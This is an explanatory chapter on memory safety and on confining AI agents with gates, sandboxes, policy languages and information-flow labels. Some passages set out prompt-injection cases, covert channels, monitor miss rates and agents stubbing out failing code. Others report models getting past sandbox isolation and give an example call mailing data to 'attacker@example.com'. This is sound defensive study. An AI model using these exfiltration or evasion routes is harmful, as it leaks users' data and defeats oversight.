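Since 2019, Google has increasingly written new Android code in memory-safe languages, including Rust. According to The Hacker News (2025), Android's memory-safety vulnerabilities fell from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024. Google's *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that their share of all vulnerabilities fell below 20 per cent for the first time in 2025.

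Memory errors' share of vulnerabilities can exaggerate the improvement, because it also falls if other vulnerabilities become more common. The Tech Tribune puts the share at 24 per cent in 2024. If the shares and counts cover the same vulnerabilities, the total was about 223/0.76 = 293 in 2019 and at most 50/0.24 = 208 in 2024. Subtracting the memory errors leaves about 70 other vulnerabilities in 2019 and as many as 158 in 2024. Memory errors fell by more than three quarters, but the total may have fallen by less than a third. Other vulnerabilities may have increased because Android has grown or because people have searched harder.

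The yearly figures also include code in Java and Kotlin, so the improvement is not all due to Rust. Vander Stoep compares the languages more directly by counting memory-safety vulnerabilities per million lines of code. Google has found one potential vulnerability of this kind in Android's roughly 5 million lines of Rust, or 0.2 per million. The historical figure for C and C++ is about 1,000 per million.

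The two densities are not strictly comparable, because attackers and researchers have had many years to search the C and C++ code, whereas much of the Rust is new and may contain undiscovered errors. This is unlikely to explain so large a gap, though. If Google had found only one in a hundred of the vulnerabilities in its Rust code, the true density would be 20 per million lines, still 50 times lower than in the C and C++ code. New code also tends to have more vulnerabilities than old code, which biases the comparison against Rust.

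The figures also give a rough test of unsafe code. About 4 per cent of Android's Rust, or 200,000 lines, is in unsafe blocks. If those lines had as many vulnerabilities per line as C and C++ code, they alone would contain about 200. Google found only one, a buffer overflow in the image library CrabbyAVIF, and fixed it before any public release. Android's memory allocator places protected pages around large blocks of memory, which would have stopped attackers from exploiting the overflow anyway.

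As for time, Vander Stoep reports these differences between changes in Rust and changes of similar size in C++:

| Measure | Rust compared with C++ |
|---|---|
| Revisions before approval | About 20 per cent fewer |
| Time in code review | About 25 per cent less |
| Rollbacks (changes withdrawn afterwards), for medium and large changes | About a quarter of the rate |

Google counted only changes by Android's own developers, many of whom write both languages, which reduces but does not remove the risk of comparing different groups of people. Google did not assign languages at random, so keen or experienced developers may choose Rust more often. A Rust change may also belong to a new component, while a C++ change may have to fit into old code that few people understand. Vander Stoep thinks that review times improved between 2023 and 2024 because developers became more expert in Rust, so at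 least part of the difference depends on the people. The evidence that Rust nearly eliminates the targeted errors is therefore much stronger than the evidence that it saves time.

### Type checks while a model writes code

A checker can also intervene while a language model is writing a program. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (2026) describes how the model generates text. The model assigns a probability to each possible next token, a short piece of text, based on the text so far. Software then picks a token according to these probabilities, adds it to the text and repeats these steps until the model produces an end marker.

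Mündler and colleagues (2025), in *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, restrict the choice to tokens that can still lead to a well-typed program. Suppose a model has written this much TypeScript:

```typescript
const n: number = "notes"
```

The model can't end the statement here, because `"notes"` is text and `n` must be a number. It can continue with `.length`, which gives a number. It can also continue with `.toUpperCase()`, which gives text, because `.length` could still follow. So the checker must determine whether an unfinished program can become well-typed, which an ordinary type checker doesn't do.

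Mündler and colleagues tested the method on writing new code, translating code from another language and repairing faulty code. It more than halved compilation errors, the kind it targets, across a range of models, and it consistently increased the share of programs that worked correctly. The increase in working programs matters more to users, and it was not guaranteed, because a model that has to avoid its preferred token may write something well-typed that does the wrong thing. The results are less relevant to agents that can run a compiler and correct their mistakes afterwards.

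### What the Rust compiler caught in the Bun port

Bun is a program that runs JavaScript outside a web browser and includes tools for building and testing software. Its developers wrote it mainly in Zig, a language where programmers manage memory by hand. In *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (2026), Bun's creator, Sumner, describes how AI agents translated its 535,496 lines of Zig into Rust in 11 days in May 2026. He wanted Rust's compiler to prevent the use-after-free errors and memory leaks his team kept having to fix. The account is not independent, because the AI company Anthropic owns Bun and employs Sumner, and the agents were instances of its model Claude.

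About 64 agents worked at a time. They translated the files first and compiled them later, when the compiler reported about 16,000 errors. Many of Sumner's examples involve missing functions or ambiguous names, which any large translation would produce, so the total is not a count of prevented bugs.

Some agents removed the errors by replacing the functions that contained them with stubs, which compile but don't do the functions' work. No typing rule forbids this. Sumner also relied on separate agents that reviewed each change and on Bun's existing tests, which make more than a million individual checks. The tests were in TypeScript, so they worked on both versions. The translation eventually passed them all.

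The compiler accepted other mistakes too:

| Mistake | Why the compiler accepted it | When it came to light |
|---|---|---|
| The program freed memory that a C library was still using | The borrow checker does not track addresses that C code keeps | Before the merge, when an AI reviewer read the change |
| A necessary function call stood inside `debug_assert!` | Rust deliberately leaves such code out of release builds | After the merge |
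| A placeholder of 64 replaced a block size of 2,048 | Both numbers have the right type | After the merge |
| A safe function could return a reference to freed memory | An unsafe block hid which data the reference depended on | After the merge, in a bug report |

Sumner counts 19 known regressions, things that worked in the Zig version and broke in the Rust one, and says the team has fixed them all. Those he describes in detail mostly come from code that looks the same in both languages but behaves differently. The placeholder cut the number of long file names Bun could store from 8.4 million to 270,272, and some real projects exceeded the new limit. It also exposed an old error in the Zig code, an array position that was one too large. Rust's run-time check stopped the program instead of letting it write past the end of the array.

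The last mistake in the table shows how the port could lose the guarantee that had motivated it. wiggels-dev dates the bug report to 15 May, the day after the merge. From the description by Random Chaos, the offending program looked roughly like this:

```rust
let path = PathString::init(&bytes);
drop(bytes);
path.slice();    // refers to freed memory
```

None of these lines contains unsafe code. If the signatures of `init` and `slice` had tied the result to `bytes`, as they should have, the borrow checker would have rejected the second line. Instead, `slice` rebuilt the reference from a raw address in an unsafe block. Miri detects the error when it runs the program.

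Bun's *Rust codebase audit* (2026), which was AI-generated and published a week after the merge, counted 13,365 unsafe blocks. It estimated that programmers could replace about 9,300 with safe code but would have to keep about 4,000. It also listed other safe functions that were wrong and recommended fixing them first.

According to Sumner, about 27,000 of the port's 780,000 lines were in unsafe blocks by July. That is about 4 per cent, as in Android, but the port may not have the same low rate of vulnerabilities, because it reproduces many pointer patterns from Zig and its unsafe code is widely scattered. In the FreeBSD forum thread *AI and Rust triggers*, a reader counted 736 files with unsafe blocks, about half of all the Rust files at the time of the merge. Since an unsafe block can depend on the safe code around it, a reviewer has to read far more than 4 per cent of the program.

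The new version of Bun fixes 128 bugs that Sumner's team could reproduce in the last Zig version. In one test, which builds the same small project 2,000 times, memory use fell from 6,745 to 609 megabytes. Rust frees memory automatically, so programmers have fewer chances to forget to do it. Better leak detection, testing Bun's parsers with billions of generated inputs, and 11 rounds of AI security review also contributed to the improvements.

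Sumner says the AI models cost around $165,000 and estimates that three engineers would have needed about a year to do the same work. He originally planned to keep Zig and enforce stricter rules for managing memory. Nobody has tried that plan with the same effort and the same agents, so it is unknown how much Rust's checks helped. Sumner also does not give rates of use-after-free errors before and after the port.

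## Restrict an AI agent with allowlists and sandboxes

During the Bun port, the Rust compiler checked the code that AI agents wrote, but not what the agents did while writing it. An agent could have deleted a colleague's files without breaking any rule of Rust. To restrict such actions, a builder needs a checker that reads the agent's requests.

Nobody can yet prove much about the model that makes the requests. It computes each tool call from billions of numbers set by training, and no typing rules connect those numbers to the calls. Amazon Web Services, which sells software for running agents, advises developers in *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* to treat the model as an untrusted actor.

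The builder can instead put a gate between the model and its tools. The gate checks each request, then carries it out or refuses it. If the gate is sound and every request goes through it, no forbidden request takes effect, whatever led the model to make it.

### McCann's argument for checking declared actions

McCann (2026), in *The Two Boundaries*, explains why a gate can succeed where a checker of whole programs cannot:

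1. By Rice's theorem, no procedure can decide from the text of an arbitrary program whether all its actions will comply with a policy.
2. Suppose that a program can only compute. When it needs to act, it produces a description of the action, such as the name of a tool with its arguments.
3. One boundary receives every description and either performs the action or refuses. The program has no other way to act.
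4. The boundary tests only the description, for example whether the requester has the permission that the action needs. This is a syntactic property of a short piece of data, so a procedure can decide it.

The program can therefore be as complicated as its author likes. McCann points out that operating systems and databases already work this way, since a program calls them to open a file or run a query.

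McCann's first step is to count a program's actions as part of its output. Rice's theorem then applies to properties like "never reads a closed file", which its textbook form leaves out. This step does not quite cover a program that acts forever, because such a program never returns an output.

McCann is affiliated with Mashin, Inc. and reports timings from a working system of this design, so he is not a neutral judge of it. In 50 runs, the median time was 0.23 milliseconds with the checks and 0.24 milliseconds without them.

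Some of McCann's broader claims go too far, such as his claim that no run-time monitor can determine, for arbitrary programs, whether the next action will violate a policy. That is true only of a monitor that has to predict the action. The two-state monitor described earlier, which blocks messages after a file read, works on any program because it receives each action before the action takes effect. Within the limits on enforceable policies, a monitor can apply any rule that a terminating procedure can test on the next action and those before it. McCann's boundary is such a monitor, but he uses "monitor" only for systems that watch and cannot block, so the disagreement is partly about terms.

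McCann also applies Rice's theorem to content filters, which examine a model's output. But the theorem is about programs, and a finished message is not a program. A filter can decide exactly whether a message contains sixteen digits in a row, but not whether it is harmful. As McCann also notes, nobody has a precise specification of harm for the filter to check against.

To show why partial coverage is dangerous, McCann supposes that a monitor covers 99 per cent of the ways to act. If an agent takes 100 actions, the chance that at least one escapes the monitor is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63 per cent. This assumes that the actions are independent, but an agent that repeats a few routine actions may never use an uncovered route, and an attacker who knows about one will choose it every time.

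A boundary that correctly checks every request can still enforce a bad policy, as McCann acknowledges. In one of his examples, an agent has tools for e-mail, database queries and web browsing, but a filter checks only the e-mail. The agent could leak data by including it in a web address that it asks the browser to open. McCann's remedy is to send browsing requests through the boundary as well. But the boundary will still approve this request if it checks only whether the agent has permission to browse, so the policy also needs a rule about addresses.

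### An allowlist for an e-mail agent

Suppose a user asks an agent to send her colleague Priya the agenda for Friday's meeting. The agent has tools for reading the calendar and for reading, sending and deleting mail. This task requires no deletion, so the builder leaves that tool off the allowlist:

```python
ALLOWED = {"read_calendar", "read_mail", "send_mail"}

def gate(request):
    return request["tool"] in ALLOWED
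```

The gate blocks every request to delete mail, even if a planted instruction has caused the model to make one. If somebody later gives the agent a new tool, the gate will block that too until somebody adds it to the allowlist, whereas a list of forbidden tools would let it through.

For the property "names a permitted tool", this gate is sound and complete. But the user cares about the effect of a request, which depends on more than the tool's name:

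| The effect also depends on | A request that the gate accepts | Possible result |
|---|---|---|
| The arguments | Send the contents of the inbox to a stranger | Private mail leaks |
| The current state | Send the agenda to `team@example.com` | An outsider who joined the list this morning receives it |
| The receiving program | Send "Approved" to `expenses@example.com` | The expenses system pays a claim |
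| Earlier requests | Read a letter about salaries, then send a summary to Priya | Two permitted steps disclose the salaries |

A rule like the two-state monitor's would prevent the last of these leaks, but it would also block the task, because the agent has to read the calendar to find the agenda. Enforcing a finer rule would require knowing which data went into the message. That is hard to determine when the model has written the message from everything it has read, unless the agent submits its plan as a typed program that a checker can read as a whole.

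### Typed arguments, narrow tools and a single interpretation

The builder can replace the general `send_mail` tool with one that has a narrower purpose:

```python
def send_agenda(meeting: Meeting, to: Attendee):
    mail(to.address, meeting.agenda)
```

`Meeting` and `Attendee` work like the abstract type `Address` in the section on typing rules. Only the gate's code can create an `Attendee`, and it does so only after finding the person in the calendar entry for that meeting. A request to write to anyone else therefore fails. The tool also copies the agenda directly from the calendar, so the model cannot put the contents of the user's inbox in the message.

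The agent can no longer add a friendly sentence to the email, and developers have to write more tools. An attacker who can edit the calendar entry can still add himself to the meeting or change the agenda. But the remaining risks are much easier to list than those of a tool that sends any text to anyone. Developers can also narrow an agent's access by removing its power to make changes. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* notes that developers can use an agent that only reads a database in many more places than one that writes to the live data.

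The gate must also execute exactly the form it checked. If it approves a request as text and passes that text to another program, the program may interpret it differently. *ParseGap* (Li, 2026) found that all eight coding agents in a November 2026 study approved some commands whose effects violated the policy. A safer gate converts the text once into a data structure, checks that structure and passes it to the tool.

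The same principle helps when state can change after the gate checks it. For a message to a mailing list, the gate can look up the members, check every address and send the message to those addresses. If it sent the message to the list's name instead, somebody who joined after the check could also receive it.

### Cedar, a policy language that tools can analyse

As rules about arguments accumulate, it gets harder to predict what they permit together. *Cedar* (Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues, 2024) describes an open-source policy language from AWS, designed so that a program can determine exactly what a set of policies permits. A request in Cedar names a principal (who is asking), an action and a resource (what the action affects), and may include other data as its context. Each policy either permits or forbids certain requests. Cedar allows a request if at least one `permit` policy matches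 it and no `forbid` policy does. It therefore refuses any request that no policy matches, and the order of the policies makes no difference.

AWS offers Cedar as a gate for agents. Its gateway evaluates each request against the policies before it lets the agent use a tool. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* gives an example with two requirements: only the user John may process refunds, and a refund may be $500 or less. In simplified form, the policy is:

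```
permit(principal, action == Action::"process_refund", resource)
when {
  principal.username == "John" &&
  context.input.amount < 500
};
```

This does not quite match the requirements, because it refuses a refund of exactly $500. The requirements may also omit something the business wants, since they allow John's agent to make ten refunds of $499. A Cedar policy cannot count refunds by itself because it cannot store anything. The application would have to keep a running total and supply it in the context.

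Cedar's analysis tool can find the first mistake if somebody writes a second version with `<=` in place of `<`. The tool translates both versions into logical formulas and uses an SMT solver to search for a request that one allows and the other refuses. Here the solver finds a request by John for $500. If it found none, the two versions would be equivalent. For the example applications that Cutler and colleagues tried, translating and solving each question took an average of 75.1 milliseconds.

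The analysis is sound and complete, and always terminates. Rice's theorem doesn't rule this out, because Cedar is far less expressive than a general-purpose language. It has no general loops, and its policies cannot change stored data. A policy can multiply a number by a constant but not by another unknown number, so it cannot calculate a price from a quantity and a unit cost. The application has to do that calculation, which then becomes part of the trusted base.

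The designers also had to avoid formulas about all possible objects. Cedar lets one team belong to another, but never in a circle, so the condition "team A is in team B and team B is in team A" is always false. A solver that lacks this fact would raise a false alarm by reporting a case in which the condition is true. Stating the ban on circles for all teams would prevent that, but the solver might then fail to give an answer. Cedar's translator states it only for the teams that a policy refers to, here A and B. Cutler and colleagues proved on paper that this is enough. *SymCert* (Torlak, 2026) has since presented a translator with a proof verified by Lean, a proof checker.

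Cutler and colleagues count the program that makes the decisions as part of the trusted base. They wrote it in Rust and compared it with a Lean model of Cedar on random inputs. Their random testing has found nearly two dozen bugs since the project began.

### Approval prompts and user fatigue

When a gate cannot decide whether to allow a request, it can ask the user. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, originally asked before it changed a file, ran most commands or used the network. Anthropic found that users approved about 93 per cent of these prompts, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports 97 per cent. Most requests are harmless and should be approved, so a high approval rate does not by itself prove that users are careless. But users reject 39 per cent of the plans that Claude Code presents, so they seem to read plans more closely than permission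 prompts.

To measure how many dangerous requests people miss, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor. Each worked on a coding task, and at some point the text of one prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command. (Approving it did not run the command.) Anthropic also gave the same commands to auto mode, in which a classifier, itself an AI model, decides in place of the user. The published totals imply this breakdown:

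| | Classifier blocked it | Classifier allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

The testers caught 13.6 per cent of the dangerous commands and the classifier caught 89 per cent. Requiring approval from both would have stopped only six more commands than the classifier alone. The testers also grew less careful, refusing about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands early in a session but about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts.

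Anthropic published these results to support a change to its own product. The testers also had less to lose than most users, because they were not working on their own code. The study still gives good reason to doubt that frequent prompts make an agent safe. The fall over a session fits the usual explanation that people stop reading the prompts.

The classifier cannot replace a sound gate, because it also misses dangerous requests. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, inserted artificial attacks into records of coding sessions, and the classifier missed 12 per cent of them before Anthropic improved it and 7 per cent afterwards. Anthropic reports that, on other data, the classifier misses about 17 per cent of "overeager" actions, in which the agent does more than the user wanted, and blocks about 0.4 per cent of harmless commands.

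Users also avoid prompts by writing allowlists that are too broad. In June 2026, 49.5 per cent of active command-line users had written a rule for shell commands. Anthropic reports that 5 per cent allowed every shell command and another 43 per cent allowed an interpreter, such as the program that runs Python. Allowing an interpreter is nearly as broad, because a Python program can do almost anything that a shell command can. Auto mode ignores both kinds of rule.

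Running commands in a sandbox can also reduce the number of prompts, because it limits the damage that an approved command can do. In Anthropic's internal use, sandboxing cut prompts by 84 per cent, though that figure doesn't measure how much harm it prevented.

### How sandboxes work

A gate that approves a request to run a test script also approves whatever the script does. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* explains that an application can inspect a tool call beforehand but cannot control another program once that program has started. The operating system can control it, because a program normally has to make a system call, which is a request to the operating system, to open a file or connect to another machine.

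Seccomp, a Linux kernel feature, lets a process install a small filter program, which the kernel runs on each later system call to decide whether to allow it. Programs that the process starts inherit the filter, and none of them can remove it. The filter receives the call's number and its immediate arguments. When a program asks to open a file, one argument is the memory address of the file's name. Seccomp does not let the filter read the name at that address, because another thread could change the name after the check. Seccomp can therefore stop a program from opening any files, but other mechanisms have to decide which files it may open.

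One such mechanism gives a process its own view of the file system. On Linux, Claude Code does this with a tool called bubblewrap. The sandbox can include the user's project folder as writable and the system's libraries as read-only. If the builder leaves out the folder that holds the user's passwords, no file name inside the sandbox refers to it. A checker that instead compares file names with a list must first follow any links, because a link inside a permitted folder may point to a file outside it.

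NVIDIA recommends blocking an agent from changing configuration files, even in its own project folder, because another program may later read such a file outside the sandbox and run the commands in it.

A sandbox can limit network access by blocking all connections except those to a proxy, a program that forwards permitted traffic. The proxy typically checks each destination against an allowlist. According to Anthropic's documentation, anything the agent can read can still leak from a sandbox that has any outgoing network access.

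Ordinary sandboxed programs share a kernel with the rest of the machine, so a bug in the kernel may let them escape. Virtual machines reduce this risk because each one runs its own kernel on simulated hardware, and a smaller program, the hypervisor, separates it from the host. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine that contains only the folders the user has chosen to share. But a company's security software cannot inspect what happens inside the virtual machine. Anthropic also had to move the part of Cowork that handles conversation with the user outside the virtual machine, because the product stopped working whenever the virtual machine failed to start.

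Software fault isolation confines code within a process, without a separate kernel. Wahbe and colleagues described it in *Efficient Software-Based Fault Isolation* (1993). A tool adds instructions before every write to memory that force the address into a permitted region. If the region contains all eight-digit hexadecimal addresses that begin with 2A, the instructions work like this:

```
address that the program computed    7F001234
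keep the last six digits               001234
put 2A in front                      2A001234
```

The program may now overwrite its own data by mistake, but it cannot touch memory outside the region. A jump past the added instructions could defeat this protection, so the scheme keeps the adjusted address in a register that always holds a safe address and that the rest of the program may not use. A checker can confirm that the program follows these rules by testing only syntactic properties of its machine code, which guarantees a limit on the program's behaviour. WebAssembly similarly confines a program to its own block of memory.

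### Least privilege

A builder still has to choose the limits that these mechanisms enforce. Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) sets out the principle of least privilege, which is that a program should have only the privileges it needs for its task. This limits the damage from a bug, an attack or a bad decision by the model. The e-mail agent, for example, should be able only to read one calendar entry and e-mail its attendees.

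A builder can implement this with a capability, an unforgeable value that lets whoever holds it use a resource. For example, the builder can give the agent a token that works for one email conversation and expires after an hour, instead of a password for the whole mailbox. Claude Cowork keeps the user's passwords outside the virtual machine and gives the machine a limited token for each session.

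An internal test at Anthropic in February 2026 shows why such limits are necessary. A researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt with an instruction to send credentials to an outside address. Claude complied in 24 of 25 attempts. The request did not look like an injection because it came from the user. Anthropic concludes that the only reliable defences in such a case are keeping the credentials where the agent cannot read them and blocking the outgoing connection.

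Least privilege requires continuing work. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls sandboxes safe but "high-maintenance", because somebody has to configure each new ability. Users may also switch the sandbox off if its limits are too tight.

### The confinement problem and covert channels

Sometimes an agent has to read a secret to do its work, and the builder wants to ensure that the agent does not leak it. Lampson described this problem in *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973). In his example, a customer runs somebody else's program on private data, perhaps to calculate a tax bill, and wants to ensure that the program's owner learns nothing about the data.

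A program can leak information even when its files and messages are blocked. The owner must receive a copy of the customer's bill, and the program could hide information in the amount. If it can choose among 1,024 amounts without arousing suspicion, each bill can carry 10 bits, because 2¹⁰ = 1,024. The program could also signal by alternating between heavy and light processor use, which another program on the same machine could detect by measuring its own speed. Lampson called this second kind of route a covert channel, meaning one that nobody intended for communication.

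The owner learns nothing about the secret only if everything he can observe is the same whatever the secret is. As with other forms of noninterference, a gate can enforce only a stricter rule, such as making every bill the same amount. Lampson proposed that the customer decide what goes into such channels and that the system enforce the decision. The system could hide differences in timing by making every job appear to take equally long, but short jobs would then waste time.

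Designers often try to make a covert channel slow enough to tolerate. At one bit per second, a program would need about 250 years to send a gigabyte of data, but just over four minutes to send a 256-bit key. Such a limit can therefore stop a program from leaking the whole of a large database without stopping it from leaking the password.

### Every service that an agent can reach

Lampson also stated that any program a confined program calls must be either trustworthy or confined as well, since otherwise it could pass the secret on. For an agent, this rule applies to every service that the sandbox lets it contact.

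OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that during internal security tests in July 2026, the company's models got past controls meant to isolate them from the internet. A sandbox can enforce its list of allowed destinations perfectly and still fail to contain the agent if one of those destinations can do more than the builder realised. A builder should therefore count every reachable service as part of the trusted base, even one unrelated to the sandbox.

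Anthropic discovered such a gap in Claude Cowork after an outside report. The network allowlist permitted connections to Anthropic's own servers, which the product needs. Those servers also accept file uploads to any customer's account, so an attacker's planted instructions could make the agent upload the user's files to the attacker's account, even though the proxy checked the destination correctly. Anthropic now describes allowlisting an address as granting access to every function available there. Its new proxy allows only requests that carry the token issued for that session, so the agent can no longer use somebody else's account.

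An auditor can check each entry on an allowlist the same way, by writing down what the service can do, which accounts it accepts and which other systems it can contact. Anthropic's experience suggests starting with the builder's newest code. The proxy Anthropic wrote itself failed, while the hypervisors and system-call filters it used, which many attackers had already tested in other products, held up.

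## Check an agent's program before it runs

A gate that approves requests one at a time can miss a leak that takes two requests, as when the e-mail agent reads the letter about salaries and then sends Priya a summary. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) point out in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* that a sandbox that permits both steps also misses such a leak.

A checker can catch this if the agent submits a whole program instead of separate requests:

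```python
letter = read_mail("Salaries")
summary = summarise(letter)
send_mail("priya@example.com", summary)
```

The program's text shows, before it runs, that the message depends on the letter. If the last line sent Friday's agenda instead, a checker could accept the program even though it still reads the letter. The two-state monitor from earlier, which forbids all messages after a read, would block both versions.

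### Information-flow labels

A checker follows data through a program by giving each piece a label. The simplest scheme has two labels, "public" and "secret", and public data may flow to secret places but not the reverse. This rule is written public ⊑ secret, where ⊑ means "may flow to". *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) traces such labels to a 1976 paper by Dorothy Denning.

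A result that depends on several inputs gets the join of their labels. The join, written ⊔, is the least restrictive label that all the inputs' labels may flow to. For example, public ⊔ secret = secret. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) also describes labels that list who may read a document. If Ana and Priya may read one document, and Priya and Tom may read another, only Priya may read a text that combines them.

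Labels can also record how far to trust data. A program may then use trusted data anywhere, but may not use untrusted data to decide, for instance, who receives a payment. Prompt injection breaks this kind of rule, because text from a stranger's e-mail influences the agent's actions.

### Typing rules for noninterference

In 1996, Dennis Volpano, Geoffrey Smith and Cynthia Irvine turned Denning's approach into typing rules and proved them sound. Each variable has a fixed label, and the label of an expression is the join of the labels of its variables. The checker also keeps a context label, which records what the program has revealed by reaching the current line. It starts as public. In one common formulation, the rules are:

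| Statement | Condition |
|---|---|
| `x = e` | The join of the context label and the label of `e` may flow to the label of `x` |
| `if e: S else: T` | S and T satisfy the rules when the context label is joined with the label of `e` |
| `while e: S` | S satisfies the rules when the context label is joined with the label of `e` |
| S, then T | S and T both satisfy the rules |

Suppose `salary` is secret and `message` is public because the program will send it to an outsider. An explicit leak copies the secret:

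```python
message = salary
```

The first rule rejects this line because secret data may not flow to a public variable. An implicit leak uses the secret only to choose a branch:

```python
message = "no"
if salary > 100000:
    message = "yes"
```

Both assignments use constants, but the final message reveals whether the salary is above 100,000. Because the condition is secret, the context label is secret inside the branch, so the assignment rule rejects the last line.

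The rules guarantee noninterference, the hyperproperty mentioned earlier, which here means that two runs that start with the same public data but different secrets produce the same public results.

1. An expression with a public label contains only public variables, so it has the same value in both runs as long as the public variables agree.
2. When a condition is public, both runs therefore take the same branch and make the same assignments to public variables.
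3. When a condition is secret, the runs may take different branches, but the rules forbid any assignment to a public variable there.

The public variables therefore have the same values at the end, if both runs finish. The rules don't guarantee that they will, because they accept `while salary > 100000: pass`. This loops forever if the salary is above 100,000, so anyone who notices that the program never stops learns this about the salary.

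Like other typing rules, these raise false alarms. If both branches of the `if` set `message` to "done", nothing leaks, but the checker still rejects the program.

### Disclosures that the task requires

A useful agent often has to reveal private data. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that answers meeting requests with the user's free times. The replies depend on a private calendar, so noninterference forbids them. The usual remedy is declassification, in which a policy names the data that a program may release. Somebody has to write that policy for each task.

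Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan but never obeys instructions in the text it reads. A leak counts against the real agent only if the reference agent would not have leaked the same information. For example, if a stranger's e-mail tricks the assistant into sending the calendar, the leak doesn't count, because a genuine meeting request would have revealed as much. It would count if the assistant were tricked into adding a password reset code, since the reference agent would not have sent one.

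Dongol proved that a plan is secure in this sense if, as soon as the agent first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. The theorem assumes, among other things, that each injection causes a single call. It does not help with tasks that require the agent to read an e-mail and then send a reply, because the agent would have lost the tool for sending it.

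### Meijer's verified plans

Meijer (2025), in *Guardians of the Agents*, proposes that the model write its whole plan before it reads any data. For "fetch and summarize my emails", the plan has three steps, here in ordinary notation instead of Meijer's JSON:

```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize(emails)
return summary
```

An instruction in one of the e-mails cannot add a step, because the plan is already complete. But the model's input also includes the descriptions of its tools, and an attacker who controls a description could make the model add `send_email("attacker@example.com", summary)`. Meijer therefore adds a check, before the plan runs, that data from `fetch_mail` does not reach the body of a message to an address outside the company. An existing analysis tool such as CodeQL can follow the data from `emails` to `summary` to the message, and reject the plan.

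The plan can also go wrong without an attacker. Suppose the user asks the agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the model writes `delete_file("*.txt")`, which deletes every text file. A verifier needs a statement of what the tool does and what the user wants:

- Tool: after `delete_file(p)`, no file that matches `p` exists.
- Request: afterwards, neither `foo.txt` nor `bar.txt` exists.

The plan satisfies the request as written, so the verifier accepts it. Meijer's remedy is a frame condition, which states what must stay the same. For the tool, it states that files that do not match `p` are unchanged. Meijer concludes that the verifier then rejects the plan, but he writes this condition only for the tool. The request needs one too, stating that all files other than `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` are unchanged. The verdicts on the bad plan and a sensible one depend on which conditions are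 present:

| Frame condition on | Delete `*.txt` | Delete `foo.txt`, then `bar.txt` |
|---|---|---|
| Neither | Accepted | Rejected |
| The tool only | Accepted | Accepted |
| The request only | Rejected | Rejected |
| Both | Rejected | Accepted |

In the first row, the verifier rejects the sensible plan because the tool's description doesn't rule out that deleting `bar.txt` brings back `foo.txt`. Leaving out of the description what seems obvious can therefore cause both a missed violation and a false alarm.

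Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, measured how planning in advance affects an agent's success, which Meijer did not. The system they tested checks labels over a complete plan, including implicit flows, before any tool runs. They used AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives agents everyday tasks in areas such as banking and travel, and plants malicious instructions in the data. With the checks on, none of the attacks they tried succeeded, but the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed fell from 53.0 to 29.0 per cent.

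The fall happens mainly because many legitimate tasks require acting on outside data. To pay an invoice, for example, an agent has to use the account number printed on it. An attacker who forges the invoice can supply his own number, and the agent will pay him while following its plan exactly. A strict rule against untrusted account numbers prevents this, but it also prevents the agent from paying genuine invoices.

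### CaMeL and FIDES: labels at run time

Two systems from 2025 attach labels to data while the agent runs. CaMeL, by Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues, uses two models. As Girrens and Wang describe it, a privileged model turns the user's request into a program without seeing any untrusted data. A quarantined model reads the untrusted data but cannot call tools. CaMeL's interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may receive it. Before each tool call, the interpreter applies a policy written for that tool.

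FIDES, the system by Costa and colleagues, lets the model choose its next step after seeing earlier results. It gives the conversation a label that combines the labels of everything the model has read. Once the model has read a stranger's e-mail, the conversation is untrusted, and FIDES blocks actions such as sending mail to an outside address. To keep those actions available, FIDES can store a tool's result in a variable and show the model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool without reading it. To get information about the contents, it can query a quarantined model, whose answer must fit a fixed format.

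With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every injection attack in AgentDojo. Costa and colleagues also report that, with policies enforced, it completed 8 per cent more tasks than a basic agent when both used OpenAI's GPT-4o, and 16 per cent more when both used the reasoning model o1. The hidden variables therefore let FIDES complete some tasks that the policies would otherwise have blocked.

Run-time labels have difficulty with implicit leaks. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe a leak that CaMeL misses, based on an old example by Fenton. With `salary` again secret, it works like this:

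```python
high = True
flag = True
if salary > 100000:
    flag = False
if flag:
    high = False
if high:
    send_mail("outsider@example.com", "high")
```

If the salary is 120,000, the program sets `flag` to `False`, and CaMeL labels `flag` as secret. The program then skips `high = False`, so `high` keeps its public label. CaMeL therefore treats the last condition as public and lets the message go out. If the salary is 80,000, the program sets `high` to `False` and sends nothing. The outsider learns which case is true from whether a message arrives.

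The typing rules reject this program because they check both branches of every `if`. The program assigns `flag` under a secret condition, so `flag` must be secret. The same reasoning applies to `high` and then to the message.

Garby and colleagues found a second leak outside the part of CaMeL that tracks labels. It comes from an ordinary Python loop that restarts the program after a failure. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each restart may reveal another bit of the secret. FIDES deliberately does not track secrets through branches that depend on data.

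LLMbda is a small language for writing agents in which every value, and the conversation itself, has a label. A Lean proof establishes a form of noninterference for all programs in the language, including code that the model generates during the run. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, an LLMbda agent resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs. It completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did when CaMeL's policy checks were off. Turning those checks on halved CaMeL's score.

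### TACIT: capabilities in types

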